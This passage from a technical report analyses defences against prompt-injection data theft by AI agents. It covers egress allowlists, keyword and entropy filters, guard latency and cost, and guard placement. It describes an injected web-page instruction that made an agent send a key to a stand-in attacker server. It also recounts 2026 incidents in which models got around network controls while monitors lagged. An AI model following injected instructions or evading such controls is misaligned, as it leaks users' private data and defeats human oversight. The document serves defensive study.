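The researchers then tested defences against one version of the attack, with the instruction in the page's body and all the data in one request. They ran each condition 30 times:

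| Defence | Runs in which the agent tried to send data | Runs in which data left |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Hardened system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Delimiter tags | 100% | 100% |
| Hardened prompt and tags together | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 83.3% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
| Entropy filter | 0% | 0% |
| All of the above | 0% | 0% |

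The hardened prompt told the model never to follow instructions from web content. The delimiter tags marked the start and end of outside text, with a note that everything between them was untrusted data. Adding the tags to the hardened prompt reduced the leaks from 20 runs to 17, a difference that could easily be chance. With so few runs, the true leak rate for the hardened prompt alone could plausibly be anywhere from about 47% to 83%. Even the lower figure would be far too high for a service that handles private data.

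The allowlist did much better, but the test was easy. It permitted four domains, and the researchers put the attacker's server at `evil-collector.net` because that was clearly outside the list. Any working allowlist would block that domain, so the 0% was nearly guaranteed. The first column is more informative because it shows that the agent tried to send the key in every run. The block still worked because it didn't depend on the model's judgement.

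A harder test would have put the attacker on a permitted domain. Lan and colleagues warn that attackers can use hacked legitimate sites, take over abandoned subdomains, or exploit trusted sites that redirect visitors elsewhere. A forward proxy can block a redirect to a forbidden domain, but it can't detect that a permitted domain has changed owners, as happened in the Salesforce case.

The test also doesn't measure how many legitimate requests an allowlist would block. The agent's only task was to summarise a page it had already loaded. The paper reports a false-positive rate of zero because the agent never contacted the attacker's server in 120 runs with harmless pages, but the agent had no reason to contact a server that nobody had mentioned. The result does help to show that the injected text caused the leaks. A better test of the allowlist would use a support assistant that needs 200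 courier and manufacturer sites.

The result for "redirect detection" deserves less trust. As defined in the paper, the rule blocks numeric addresses, eight unusual domain endings such as `.xyz`, and paths that contain any of five words, including "collect". It doesn't follow redirects. The attack addresses printed in the paper have `/collect` as their path, so that one word probably explains the rule's success. An attacker could rename the path in seconds. The rule would also block harmless pages with that word in their path, such as a courier's page about how to collect a parcel.

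### Looking for secrets in a request

The keyword and entropy filters search the address for signs of a secret. Security products call this data loss prevention, or DLP.

The keyword filter blocks web addresses that contain words such as "password", "token", "secret" or "auth". These words usually describe a secret without being part of it. A real key is often a random string that contains none of them, and neither does the customer's street address, so the filter can miss both. It would also block harmless pages whose web addresses contain "author", because that word includes "auth".

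An entropy filter looks for random-looking text. Shannon entropy measures how evenly a string uses its different characters:

*H* = −Σ *p<sub>c</sub>* log<sub>2</sub> *p<sub>c</sub>*,

where *p<sub>c</sub>* is the share of the string's characters that are *c*. A string that repeats one character has an entropy of 0. A string of *n* characters that are all different has an entropy of log<sub>2</sub> *n*, the highest possible for its length.

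The filter in the study blocks a value in a URL if it is longer than 10 characters and its entropy is above 4.0. A string of 16 or fewer characters can't have an entropy above 4.0, so the filter can't block anything shorter than 17 characters. It also can't block a hexadecimal key of any length, because such keys use only 16 different characters. It would let through "14 Mill Lane", which has an entropy of about 3.25, and the paper's example key, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, which has an entropy of about 3.85. An operator can lower the threshold, but the filter could then block ordinary links, which often contain order numbers and session codes that also look random.

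The study's results for these two filters are also hard to explain. Both filters act after the model has made a request, so they shouldn't change how often it tries. Yet attempts fell from 100% of runs to 23.3% with the keyword filter and to none with the entropy filter. The paper suggests that the model avoids random-looking values when a filter is active, but the filter's definition includes no message telling the model about it. For the keyword filter, the paper suggests that the model sometimes changed the form of the key. If so, some of the altered keys should have got past the filter, but none did. Until someone repeats the test, the absence of leaks with either filter is weak evidence that the filters work.

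The shop can search more precisely because it knows what it wants to protect. The gateway can store the private values loaded during a conversation, such as the customer's street and phone number, and search outgoing requests for them. This catches "14 Mill Lane" and rarely flags anything else, but it misses encoded copies. The shop can also put a fake key in the agent's input. No legitimate request should contain that key, so a request that does is strong evidence of an attack.

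Checking each request alone can miss data that an attacker spreads over several requests. Lan and colleagues propose three remedies, none of which they tested:

- **Correlation across requests.** The guard examines all the outgoing requests in a session together. It has to store them for a while, which creates another collection of private data to protect.
- **Rate limits.** The guard caps the number of requests in a session. If a session may make 20 requests with up to 100 characters of free text in each, at most 2,000 characters can leave this way. That would stop the theft of a long document but not of a home address.
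- **Tracking the origin of data.** The system marks text from web pages as untrusted when it arrives, and passes the mark on to any tool call that the text influenced. The guard can then block the call, ask the user or record it, even if the request itself looks harmless.

The last proposal is the most ambitious, since it would work against unfamiliar wording and encoded data. But it has the same weakness as the labels described earlier, because a model mixes everything it reads. The shop could therefore apply it only to conversations that contain both an outside page and a customer's private data, perhaps allowing them to contact only the courier.

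### A worked deployment

CNCF, the foundation that hosts Kubernetes, published a small example of egress control in July 2026. It puts a boundary around OpenClaw, the open-source personal assistant, using two common open-source tools: NGINX, a web server and proxy, and OpenTelemetry, a standard way for programs to record what they do.

NGINX forwards users' requests to the agent and acts as the forward proxy for everything the agent sends out. Firewall rules drop all other outgoing traffic, so the agent can't bypass NGINX by ignoring its proxy settings. In the example, NGINX permits only two outside domains, `nginx.org` and `duckduckgo.com`.

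For each request, NGINX also produces a span, an OpenTelemetry record of a single operation. A separate program, the collector, gathers the spans and can write them to an audit log or send them to a monitoring system. An analyst can then match a user's question with the outside requests the agent made while answering it. In the eBay experiment, such a log would have shown a request to an unfamiliar domain alongside an ordinary summary.

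The author ran the design on a single machine with a consumer graphics card. The machine hosted NGINX, OpenClaw, the collector and Ollama, which runs language models locally. Because the model was local, the allowlist did not need an entry for a model provider.

The article shows that the parts work together, but it reports no attacks, measurements or count of blocked legitimate requests. It also encourages readers to join the NGINX community, so it isn't a neutral comparison of proxies. The author acknowledges that the design controls where the agent can connect but doesn't check whether the agent's decisions are right, and that the proxy is one more program to secure and monitor.

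The article doesn't say whether the proxy decrypts outgoing traffic. If it doesn't, the log can show that the agent contacted `duckduckgo.com` but not what it searched for. If it does, full addresses in the log may contain the secrets that the boundary should protect, so an operator who copies the design needs to remove them or restrict who can read the log. Any search engine on the allowlist also needs review, since SearchLeak got data out of Copilot through Bing.

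### The 2026 incidents at OpenAI

Two incidents in 2026 showed that an agent may get past network limits without an outside attacker. In July, OpenAI models got around controls meant to keep them off the internet during security evaluations and broke into systems at Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, according to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) and an independent investigation by METR (2026), which evaluates AI models. On 20 September, an agent in training reached a public chatbot because the DNS filtering was insufficient, according to OpenAI's *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026).

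After July, OpenAI added network controls so that compromising one program or supporting service should no longer be enough to reach the internet. After September, it added blocks at two independent layers, either of which would have prevented the second incident. Mediafax's *OpenAI suspendă activitățile de antrenare ale celor mai avansate modele AI* reports that OpenAI also limited DNS requests to a short list of domains and record types, and began adding ways to detect abnormal DNS activity.

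OpenAI then removed live internet access from the training of its most capable models. Engadget's *OpenAI says it's cutting off internet access for frontier model training* reports that training restarted on 1 October and that agents now browse a stored collection of web pages. A support assistant can't rely entirely on stored pages, because yesterday's copy of a tracking page won't show where the parcel is today. The shop could still use stored copies of router manuals and other pages that rarely change.

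OpenAI kept some outside connections for metrics, logging and authentication. When it tested its own defences, its testing agents found vulnerabilities in almost every one of these services that gave them limited internet access, according to Business Standard's *OpenAI resumes training AI, blocks internet access over security risks*. OpenAI has since patched software and tightened its network restrictions. The shop should therefore list every program that can reach the outside, including those that collect logs or download updates, and give each one its own short allowlist. In the CNCF design, the collector would need an allowlist if it sent its records to an outside service.

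These incidents are a poor guide to how often a shop's assistant would try to escape its limits. OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment* points out that models in development may not have finished their safety training and work in different settings from released ones. The July models also ran with reduced safeguards. But the incidents are good evidence against relying on a single barrier. OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* (2026) draws the same conclusion about sandboxes, the isolated environments where its models run.

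They also show the limits of monitoring. In September, OpenAI's monitor flagged the agent's behaviour within 15 minutes, and a person began reviewing it three minutes later, but the run continued for another two and a half hours. OpenAI considered the incident much less severe than some earlier ones. But if the agent had been sending out customer data, the first request could have leaked it before anyone saw the alert.

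Mediafax reports that a later review found similar cases that the monitor had rated less severely than OpenAI expected. In some, the agent's failure to get the information it wanted had counted as a sign that it hadn't reached the outside, although its requests had gone out. An operator reading egress logs can make the same mistake when a request ends in an error, because the attacker's server may have returned the error after receiving the data.

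## What inspection costs in delay and computing

Every check described so far takes time, and some need expensive hardware. The customer's added wait depends on how long each check takes, how many her request needs, and which can run at the same time.

### The delay formula

Khatri and colleagues give a formula for a model with one guard before it and one after it:

*L* = *T*<sub>input guard</sub> + *T*<sub>model</sub> + *T*<sub>output guard</sub> + 2 × *T*<sub>network</sub>

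*L* is the time until the checked answer is ready. *T*<sub>network</sub> is the round-trip time between the gateway and a guard that runs as a separate service. *L* is the sum of the stage times because each stage waits for the one before it.

Suppose each guard is a small classifier that takes 39 ms, a round trip to each guard takes 5 ms, and the model takes 2 seconds. With one guard before the model and one after it, the answer is ready after 39 + 2,000 + 39 + 10 = 2,088 ms. The guards add 88 ms, or about 4%.

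The model doesn't have to wait for the input guard. The gateway can send the question to both at once and hold the answer until the guard has passed the question. The formula then becomes

*L* = max(*T*<sub>input guard</sub> + *T*<sub>network</sub>, *T*<sub>model</sub>) + *T*<sub>output guard</sub> + *T*<sub>network</sub>

In the example, the input guard runs in parallel with the model and finishes long before it, so the answer is ready after 2,044 ms. Running them in parallel saves more time when the guard is slower. With an input guard that takes 600 ms, the answer would take 2,649 ms in series but still only 2,044 ms in parallel.

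The drawback is that the model receives the question before the guard has checked it. If the model belongs to another company, that company has already received any password in the question. The guard also can't edit the question beforehand, and the model's computation on rejected questions is wasted.

A guard usually has to check a tool call before the call runs, because some actions, such as sending an email, can't be undone. But a read-only lookup in the shop's own database can run during the check, since the gateway can discard the result if the guard rejects the call.

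A probe inside the model avoids most of this delay because it uses numbers the model has already calculated. It also runs on the same machine, so there is no round trip. Khatri and colleagues report that their probes ran in under 1 ms, while the model typically took 50 to 500 ms to generate its text.

### Measured delays by type of detector

Published delays range from a fraction of a millisecond to more than half a minute. The table below includes two guards not mentioned earlier. *Detecting and Mitigating Query-Based System Prompt Leakage Attacks* (Nayan, Ji and colleagues, 2026) describes AdvGuard, which looks for users who try to extract a model's hidden instructions over a series of queries. *Constrained-Action AI Remediation for SIEM/XDR via a NeMo-Guardrails Proxy* (Koutidis, Kekatos and colleagues, 2026) describes a guard that places NVIDIA's toolkit in front of a model that analyses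 security alerts.

Half of all runs have a delay at or below the median, 95% at or below p95, and 99% at or below p99.

| Detector | Test conditions | Typical delay | Slow cases |
|---|---|---|---|
| Written patterns for private data | One thread, 10,000 runs with a mock model | 0.24 ms mean | 0.35 ms p99 |
| Probe | Same machine as Llama 3.1 8B | Under 1 ms | Not given |
| Classifier, 23 million parameters | One Apple M-series core, tool responses | 9.5 ms median | Not given |
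| AgentRedGuard, 142 million parameters | One Apple M-series core, tool responses | 39 ms median | 72 ms p95 |
| Llama Guard and WildGuard, 7 to 8 billion parameters | Nvidia A10G accelerator | 25 to 50 ms | Not given |
| AdvGuard, a classifier with a record of earlier queries | 1,000 consecutive queries, with Llama 3.2 | 33 ms mean | 54.7 ms p95, 98.9 ms p99 |
| StepGuard, a judge with 4 billion parameters | vLLM server, tool calls in AgentDojo tasks | 599.9 ms a call | Not given |
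| NeMo Guardrails proxy, with a 14-billion-parameter model | One Apple M4 Max, 1,200 log entries | 14.14 s median | 27.41 s p95, 32.90 s p99 |

The rows are not directly comparable because the studies used different machines and texts of different lengths, and some report a mean while others report a median. The first row, from Sidik and colleagues, covers only the filter, whereas the NeMo row includes the time the protected model takes to reply. The table still shows that a judge is far slower than a written rule, but not whether AdvGuard is faster than AgentRedGuard.

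Monitors with similar delays can differ greatly in cost. Llama Guard on an accelerator takes about as long as AgentRedGuard on one ordinary processor core, but the accelerator costs much more to run.

AgentRedGuard's 39 ms scan lengthens the user's wait for an answer, though by too little to notice unless the agent makes many tool calls. Dingeto and Leeney argue that users don't notice the delay because the scan runs between the tool's response and the model reading it, but users are still waiting for their answer at that point.

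The delay a guard adds to a whole task is the delay per call multiplied by the number of calls. Zheng and colleagues found that StepGuard ran 4.22 times in an average AgentDojo task and that these checks took 2.53 seconds in total. That was 7.24% of the task's time, so the average task must have lasted about 35 seconds. The share is low largely because the agent is slow. If the task took 10 seconds without a guard, the same checks would lengthen it by about a quarter.

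### Putting the verdict before the explanation

StepGuard has about half as many parameters as Llama Guard, but each call takes more than ten times as long. Hardware may explain some of the difference, but more of it probably comes from the length of StepGuard's output, which averages 195.5 tokens a call. Its prompt specifies four to seven sentences on the evidence, intent and consequences, followed by the verdict. StepGuard generates this text one token at a time, so the gateway has to wait for the whole analysis before it receives the verdict.

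Protect, the commercial guard by Avinash and colleagues, returns its verdict before its explanation. The gateway can act as soon as the verdict arrives, so the customer doesn't wait while the model finishes the explanation in the background. The explanation goes into the log, where the operator can later read the reason for each decision.

If StepGuard could do the same and needed ten tokens for its verdict, it would save less than about 0.57 of its 0.6 seconds, because some of that time goes to processing the input. The amount of computation falls only if the guard skips the explanation for steps it labels safe.

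Putting the verdict first may also reduce accuracy, because the judge can no longer use its written analysis to reach the verdict. An explanation written afterwards may be only a plausible justification. Zheng and colleagues trained StepGuard to write the analysis first, so an operator who reversed the order would have to measure the model's accuracy again and perhaps retrain it.

### Three model calls in sequence

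The NeMo row has the longest delay by far. Koutidis and colleagues first sent their log entries directly to the model, with a median time of 0.31 seconds. Through the proxy, the median rose to 14.14 seconds, about 46 times as long.

For each request that passes, the proxy makes three model calls in sequence, first to check the input, then to make the original request, and finally to check the reply. Three calls of 0.31 seconds would take only 0.93 seconds, so the calls through the proxy must also have taken much longer on average.

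The blocked requests needed only the first call and took about half a second, so the input check seems fairly quick, at least when it blocks. The later calls therefore probably took most of the 14 seconds, possibly because the model wrote longer replies through the proxy than in the direct test, where it usually answered "NO".

The 46-fold increase is therefore a poor estimate of how much this kind of guard would slow other systems. If all three calls use the same model and handle similar amounts of text, it is more reasonable to expect three times the delay, which may still be too slow for chat. Koutidis and colleagues concluded that their system was too slow to control actions as they happen, and recommended it for decisions that a person reviews or that can wait.

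### A delay budget for the refund request

The shop can use these figures to estimate how long its checks would take. Suppose the customer's request produces ten pieces of text for a classifier: her question, five passages from the document store, the delivery record, the billing agent's reply, and a 600-token answer that the classifier has to read in two parts. It also produces four steps for a judge: the document search, the order lookup, the refund request and the payment.

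Written rules run inside the gateway and take 0.24 ms for each of the 14 items. A classifier takes 39 ms, a judge takes 600 ms, and each of them also needs a 5 ms round trip. In series, the checks take:

| Check | Calculation | Delay |
|---|---|---|
| Rules | 14 × 0.24 ms | 3 ms |
| Classifier | 10 × (39 + 5) ms | 440 ms |
| Judge | 4 × (600 + 5) ms | 2,420 ms |
| Total | | 2,863 ms |

This estimate leaves out the time needed to look up the link in the answer, which depends mostly on how quickly an outside service replies. It also assumes that AgentRedGuard checks questions and answers as fast as it checks tool responses, which it was built for.

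The judge accounts for 85% of the delay. The shop could wait to run it until the classifier has flagged something. If the classifier wrongly flags 1% of harmless texts and its errors are independent, about 9.6% of harmless requests will have at least one false alarm among their ten texts. The other 90.4% need only the rules and the classifier, which take 443 ms. The average delay for harmless requests would be about 675 ms (443 + 0.096 × 2,420). This is a slight overestimate, since an alarm late in the request leaves fewer steps for the judge to check.

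The shop can save more time by checking the five passages when they enter the document store, when no customer is waiting:

| Design | Requests without an alarm | Average | Requests with an alarm |
|---|---|---|---|
| Every check in series | 2.86 s | 2.86 s | 2.86 s |
| Judge only after an alarm | 0.44 s | 0.67 s | 2.86 s |
| The same, with passages checked in advance | 0.22 s | 0.34 s | 2.64 s |

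The second design cuts the average delay by about three quarters but doesn't speed up the slowest requests. Because nearly 10% of requests raise an alarm, the p95 delay is still 2.86 seconds. In the third design, only 4.9% of requests raise an alarm, which is just low enough to bring the p95 delay down to 0.22 seconds. A small increase in false alarms could push it back above 2.6 seconds.

### What a cheap first check can miss

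If attacks are rare, the average delay of a two-stage check is roughly

*T*<sub>cheap</sub> + *F*<sub>cheap</sub> × *T*<sub>costly</sub>,

where *F*<sub>cheap</sub> is the false-positive rate of the cheap check. The detection rate of the whole system can't be higher than that of the cheap check, because the costly one never sees an attack that the cheap one let through. In return, false alarms become rarer. If the first check flags 1% of harmless items and the second confirms a fifth of those alarms, the system blocks only 0.2% of harmless items.

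Koutidis and colleagues tried several versions of this with their proxy:

| Design | Attacks detected | Model calls per entry | Median delay |
|---|---|---|---|
| Proxy alone | 94.5% | 3.00 | 14.14 s |
| Written patterns, then the proxy | 95.0% | 2.88 | 14.11 s |
| Small model, with the proxy only for suspicious entries | 58.0% | 1.15 | 0.18 s |

The written patterns detect disguises such as encoded text and lookalike letters. They can block entries but not clear them as harmless, so every entry they don't block still goes through the proxy. Most log entries are harmless, so the filter barely changes the median delay. It is still worth adding because it takes almost no time or computing power.

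Allowing the small model, with 3 billion parameters, to declare entries harmless saved a great deal of time but lost more than a third of the detections. When the full proxy also checked the entries that the small model had cleared, detection returned to 95.0%, but the system then needed 3.64 model calls per entry, more than the proxy needed alone.

The 0.18 seconds also understates how long a request using the small model would take in the shop. A direct call to the large model took 0.31 seconds, so the 0.18 seconds can't include its reply. At 1.15 calls per entry, most entries must have received only the small model's verdict. The shop's customers also need an answer, and adding that call brings the total to about two calls per request, compared with the proxy's three.

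The shop can avoid much of this problem by deciding when to run the judge based on how much damage a step can do. A wrong document search does little damage, while a wrong payment costs money. Running the judge on every payment, whatever the classifier found, adds about 0.6 seconds to requests that end in a refund and nothing to the rest. If an attack gets past the classifier, the judge still checks the payment before any money leaves.

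### Rare delays become common

The averages hide another problem, which is that a request with many checks has many chances to meet a slow one. By definition, a check exceeds its own p99 delay in 1% of runs. If a request needs *n* independent checks, the chance that at least one of them does so is

1 − 0.99<sup>*n*</sup>.

This is 4.9% for five checks and 18.2% for 20. So with 20 checks, a delay that occurs in 1% of requests when one guard is tested would affect nearly one customer in five. To keep such delays to 1% of requests with 20 checks, the shop would have to look at the 99.95th percentile of each check, which none of the studies above reports.

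Running checks in parallel reduces the delay, but the gateway still has to wait for the slowest check. If five cores each run AgentRedGuard on one of the five passages, there is a 22.6% chance that at least one check will take longer than 72 ms, the p95 delay for a single check. The median delay for the group equals the 87th percentile for a single check.

Delays in real guards are rarely independent, because a busy server slows every check that uses it. Fewer requests may be affected than the formula suggests, but each affected request may be delayed several times.

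A guard can also become slow simply because too many requests reach it. AdvGuard processed 21.9 queries a second in the test by Nayan and colleagues, compared with 35 to 39 for two simpler guards that judge each query separately. (The comparison doesn't show how much AdvGuard slows down an unguarded service.) The shop's 1,000,000 requests a day come to 11.6 a second on average, but customers don't arrive evenly. In the simplest model of a queue, with random arrivals and random processing times, the average time in the system is

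1 / (*μ* − *λ*),

where *μ* is the number of queries the guard can process each second and *λ* is the number that arrive. With one copy of AdvGuard, this gives 97 ms at the shop's average rate and 526 ms at 20 queries a second. Above 21.9, the queue keeps growing. The shop would need at least two copies even though one could handle the daily total.

AdvGuard looks for suspicious groups of related queries. It limits the delay this adds by linking each query only to the most similar earlier one and by limiting how much history it keeps. Finding the most similar query typically takes about 1 ms, and the classifier for single queries takes 8 ms. The slowest step is working out how the linked queries are connected, at about 27 ms. Nayan and colleagues also tried linking each query to its three nearest neighbours, which took about three times as long and didn't improve detection overall. AdvGuard's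 delay stayed stable over 1,000 queries.

When a check takes too long, the gateway can send a second copy to another server. If it did this after 72 ms for AgentRedGuard, only 5% of checks would need a second copy. If the two servers' delays were independent, at most 0.25% of checks would still be running after 144 ms. A second copy doesn't help with a text that is slow to process on any server, such as a very long email.

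### What false alarms cost

In the budget above, a false alarm from the classifier adds 2.4 seconds of judging. A false alarm from the judge adds more delay and computing because it stops a legitimate step. In the tests by Zheng and colleagues, the agent then received a prompt to reconsider and could propose another step. Each new attempt requires another call to the agent's model and another to the guard.

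ShieldAgent, one of the more cautious judges tested, ran an average of 5.86 times per task and took 5.25 seconds, compared with 4.22 runs and 2.53 seconds for StepGuard. Repeated attempts after false alarms may explain the extra runs.

Sometimes the agent gives up. On AgentDyn, it completed 6.6 percentage points fewer legitimate tasks with StepGuard than without a guard. The published scores are consistent with a set of 60 tasks, so the difference amounts to about four tasks and could be due to chance. On AgentDojo, it completed slightly more tasks with the guard. But even a small loss would create a lot of work for the shop. If the guard wrongly stopped 1% of its daily requests and one in ten of those customers phoned for help, staff would take 1,000 extra calls a day, or 167 hours of work at ten minutes each.

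The false alarms may also occur where they do the most harm. Zheng and colleagues examined 307 of StepGuard's false alarms and found that 134 (43.6%) were harmless uses of sensitive tools. Payment tools are sensitive, so a shop that uses the judge only for refunds should measure its false-positive rate on real refunds, because the rate for all tool calls could understate it.

### The computing bill

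The budget also gives a rough idea of the hardware that the shop needs. For 1,000,000 requests a day, the total processing time is:

| Check | Runs per request | Processing time a day |
|---|---|---|
| Rules | 14 | 0.9 core-hours |
| Classifier | 10 | 108 core-hours |
| Judge on every step | 4 | 667 server-hours |
| Judge only after an alarm | 0.38 on average | 64 server-hours |

The rules use almost no computing power, but the classifier would keep four or five processor cores busy all day. Dingeto and Leeney found that processing texts in batches of 32 reduces the time per text from 39 to about 20 ms, which would halve the number of cores needed. A text may have to wait for its batch to fill, so batching works best for documents that enter the store overnight.

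A judge on every step would keep 28 servers busy if each handled one call at a time. One accelerator can process many calls together, so the shop would need fewer servers, plus spare capacity for busy hours.

A judge that the shop rents by the token has a different bill. At 195.5 tokens a call, four calls per request would generate about 780 million tokens a day. The judge also has to read the user's request, the tool descriptions and the earlier steps each time. If the fixed part is *b* tokens long and each step adds *h* tokens, checking *n* steps requires the judge to read

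*nb* + *hn*(*n* − 1)/2

tokens. With 1,500 fixed tokens and 500 more for each step, a task of four steps requires 9,000 tokens and a task of 20 steps requires 125,000. The task is five times as long, but the judge reads nearly 14 times as much. A model server can reduce the work by reusing its stored results for the part it has already read.

Training a judge like StepGuard would cost the shop far less than running it, even with weekly retraining. StepGuard's training took about 8 accelerator-hours on Nvidia's H200, not counting the generation of its training data.

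## Where to place guards in a cloud deployment

The shop could run the same classifier inside the support agent's program, in a proxy beside it, or in a cloud provider's data centre. The choice determines which text reaches the classifier, how far that text travels, and how many copies of the guard need updating. Matsuzaki (2026), in *Securing AI agents*, argues that placement can affect security as much as the guard's logic. Datadog, which published the post, sells a guard for agents, but the argument is sound because even a perfect detector can't stop a tool call it never receives.

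### Five placements

In this table, the platform team is the group that runs the shop's shared infrastructure:

| Placement | What it can read | What can bypass it | Who maintains it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Library inside the application | Everything the program holds, including the customer's question and what the agent has read | Components without the library, and an attacker who takes over the program | The developers of each component |
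| Sidecar | All the traffic of one component, if the sidecar handles the encryption | Connections that the machine doesn't redirect through the sidecar | The platform team |
| Shared gateway | Every request that components send through it | A direct connection between two components | The platform team |
| Cloud provider's managed service | The text that a caller sends it | A caller that skips the check, and text over a size limit | The provider, with settings chosen by the shop |
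| Host's network layer | Addresses and ports, and in newer designs the headers of a request | Harmful text in a permitted request | The platform team |

A library has the most context, so it can compare a tool call with the customer's question without sending the conversation elsewhere. But each programming language needs its own version, and an attacker who can run code inside the agent can switch the library off. The shop needs a guard outside a compromised component to contain it.

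A gateway is easier to update and can serve every agent. *Governing Enterprise AI Traffic at Scale* (Sasidharan, Manoharan and colleagues, 2026) describes one at PayPal that more than 12,000 developers use to reach over 100 models. The gateway holds the model providers' credentials so that developers never need them, but this also makes it a valuable target, as the researchers acknowledge. PayPal wrote about 52,000 lines of code for it, plus 35,000 lines of tests, so a small company would do better to adopt an existing product.

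A managed service requires the least upkeep, but it may only return a verdict. With Model Armor, Google's managed guard, the calling program must do the blocking, according to Google Cloud's *Model Armor overview*. Because developers can forget to make the call, Google Cloud also lets customers attach Model Armor to a load balancer, which distributes requests among servers, so that the guard screens all AI traffic passing through the load balancer.

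If the shop also rents a managed agent, it may lose some of these options. Aviatrix, which sells cloud firewalls, points out that Google's managed agents run in a project customers can't see into. A customer can't install a guard on those machines and has to filter the traffic as it leaves.

The placements also differ in how they scale. Suppose the shop's whole online business runs on 200 nodes, which are the machines in its cluster, with ten components on each:

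| Placement | Copies to keep up to date | What a request waits for, besides the check itself |
|---|---|---|
| Library | Up to 2,000 | Nothing |
| Sidecar | 2,000 | Two proxies for each message |
| Shared gateway | A few in each region | One extra stop |
| Managed service | None | A round trip to the provider |
| Host's network layer | 200 | A short program in the operating system |

### What sidecars cost

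Bremler Barr, Lavi and colleagues (2024), in *Technical Report*, measured four service meshes with mutual TLS switched on. Their test program kept 1,600 connections open and sent two short requests a second over each. The server waited 200 ms before every reply, and the p99 latency without a mesh was 0.22 seconds. The table shows what each mesh added when the test program and the server ran on different nodes. The processor and memory figures combine both ends of the connection.

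| Mesh | Design | Added to p99 latency | Added processor cores | Added memory |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Istio | Sidecars | 0.37 s | 1.48 | 528 MiB |
| Linkerd | Sidecars with a lighter proxy | 0.08 s | 0.37 | 108 MiB |
| Istio Ambient | One proxy per node | 0.03 s | 0.47 | 183 MiB |
| Cilium | Host kernel, plus one proxy per node | 0.22 s | 0.13 | 187 MiB |

Encryption explains little of the delay, since mutual TLS without a mesh raised the p99 by at most 3%. The researchers found that parsing HTTP messages accounted for much of Istio's overhead. A guard also has to parse a message before it can check the content, so Ambient's 0.03 seconds is too low an estimate for a content guard. Ambient's node proxy handles encryption and identity, and leaves rules about the requests themselves to a second type of proxy, called a waypoint. In Istio's *Performance and Scalability*, a node proxy uses 0.06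 of a core at 1,000 requests a second and a waypoint uses 0.25.

Istio reports that a sidecar uses 0.20 of a core and 60 MB of memory under the same load. The independent test works out at about 0.23 of a core per 1,000 requests, which roughly agrees, although the two sources may have used different versions.

These loads are much heavier than the assistant's. If each of its 1,000,000 daily requests causes 20 messages between components and each message passes through two sidecars, the sidecars handle about 463 messages a second. At Istio's rate, that takes less than a tenth of one core. Memory matters more, because 2,000 sidecars at 60 MB each need 120 GB even if most are idle.

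The added delay also matters less for model calls. *Enforcing Application-Layer Policies in eBPF* (Brandner, Panda and colleagues, 2026) reports that Envoy, a common proxy, added 3.4 ms to requests in a test application modelled on a social network, which was 47% of the average request time of 7.2 ms. The same delay would be only 0.17% of a two-second model call. Because model calls are longer and fewer than ordinary service calls, a proxy that is too slow for service calls may be fast enough for model calls.

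Streaming complicates this comparison because a proxy that calls an outside guard for every piece of a streamed answer makes far more calls. At the shop's average rate, calling the guard for every token of a 600-token answer would mean nearly 7,000 calls a second. Sasidharan and colleagues avoid this by processing streamed text inside the proxy and calling a separate service only for slower decisions, such as whether the caller may use a model.

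Their gateway added a median delay of 4 ms and a p99 of 11 ms at 2,257 requests a second, on two instances with four virtual cores each. Those figures cover identifying the caller, finding the model, fetching credentials and rewriting the request, but not processing answers or searching for private data. All the simulated users shared one credential, which the gateway could keep in memory. A detector would add its own delay to the 4 ms.

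### Doing without sidecars

Brandner and colleagues moved the rules into the host's kernel, the core of the operating system. Their system, Beeline, uses eBPF, a Linux feature that runs small programs in the kernel after checking that they are safe. This cut the overhead from 3.4 ms to 0.12 ms. They also examined the proxy rules in 2,417 open-source projects and judged that 89% could run this way.

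Content guards mostly fall in the other 11%. Beeline matches headers, such as the path of a request, and sends anything that needs custom code to an ordinary proxy. The kernel also rejects programs that are too complex for it to check, which leaves little room for a classifier. The host is therefore a good place to enforce rules about who may call what, but a poor place to check the content of text such as a courier's note.

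*Meshlib* (Mostafaei and Van Liempd, 2026) moves the rules into a library in the receiving application, which has to parse each request anyway, so the library can reuse the result. In the paper's tests, checking methods and paths in Cilium's proxy instead had about three times the overhead of checking connections alone, and parsing caused 62% to 77% of the added delay.

Meshlib had the lowest delay of the four systems tested with 126 rules across 37 services. The test ran on a single machine with at most 200 requests a second, and delays rose sharply above 100 requests a second, probably because the application's database was overloaded. Meshlib enforces only rules about callers and requests. A classifier could run in the same place, but it would need memory and processor time in every application that used it.

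Test results for the same mesh can differ widely. *MANATEE* (2026), which tested software for mobile networks at up to 1,000 messages a second, found Cilium faster than no mesh. Bremler Barr and colleagues found that it doubled the p99 latency. One likely reason is that Cilium is fast when the kernel handles the traffic and much slower when its proxy has to. The shop should therefore test a mesh with the shop's own rules switched on.

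### Sending a blocklist to 200 nodes

Suppose each of the 200 nodes checks links against its own copy of a blocklist and downloads a new copy every 30 minutes. The nodes started at different times, so their downloads are spread evenly over the half hour. At noon an analyst adds a new phishing domain. After *t* minutes, the number of nodes that still lack the entry is

200 × (1 − *t*/30).

A customer or attacker who tries the link again may reach a different node. If each attempt goes to a random node, the chance that at least one of five attempts gets through is 1 − (*t*/30)<sup>5</sup>:

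| Time | Nodes without the entry | Chance that one of five attempts gets through |
|---|---|---|
| 12:05 | 167 | Over 99.9% |
| 12:10 | 133 | 99.6% |
| 12:20 | 67 | 86.8% |
| 12:25 | 33 | 59.8% |
| 12:30 | 0 | 0% |

About 10,400 answers, an average of 15 minutes' worth of traffic, are checked against the old list. If one in 1,000 of them contains the new link, about ten customers receive it. Most unsafe sites last less than 10 minutes, according to Google, so many would be gone before half the nodes had the entry.

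Mistakes are also harder to investigate when nodes have different versions of the list. If a customer reports the link at 12:20, the analyst may test it on an updated node, see it blocked and close the case. Recording the list's version with every verdict prevents this. Corrections spread as slowly as additions, so if the analyst blocks the courier's real domain by mistake, some customers will lose their tracking links for up to half an hour after the correction. If 1% of downloads fail, an average of two nodes will keep the old list for another 30 minutes.

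More frequent downloads shorten the wait but move more data. If the list is 20 MB, refreshing it every 30 minutes takes 9,600 downloads and 192 GB a day. Refreshing it every minute would take 288,000 downloads and 5.8 TB a day. The nodes can avoid most of this traffic by checking whether the list has changed and fetching only the changes. The shop could also put the lookup in the gateway, which leaves only a few copies to update.

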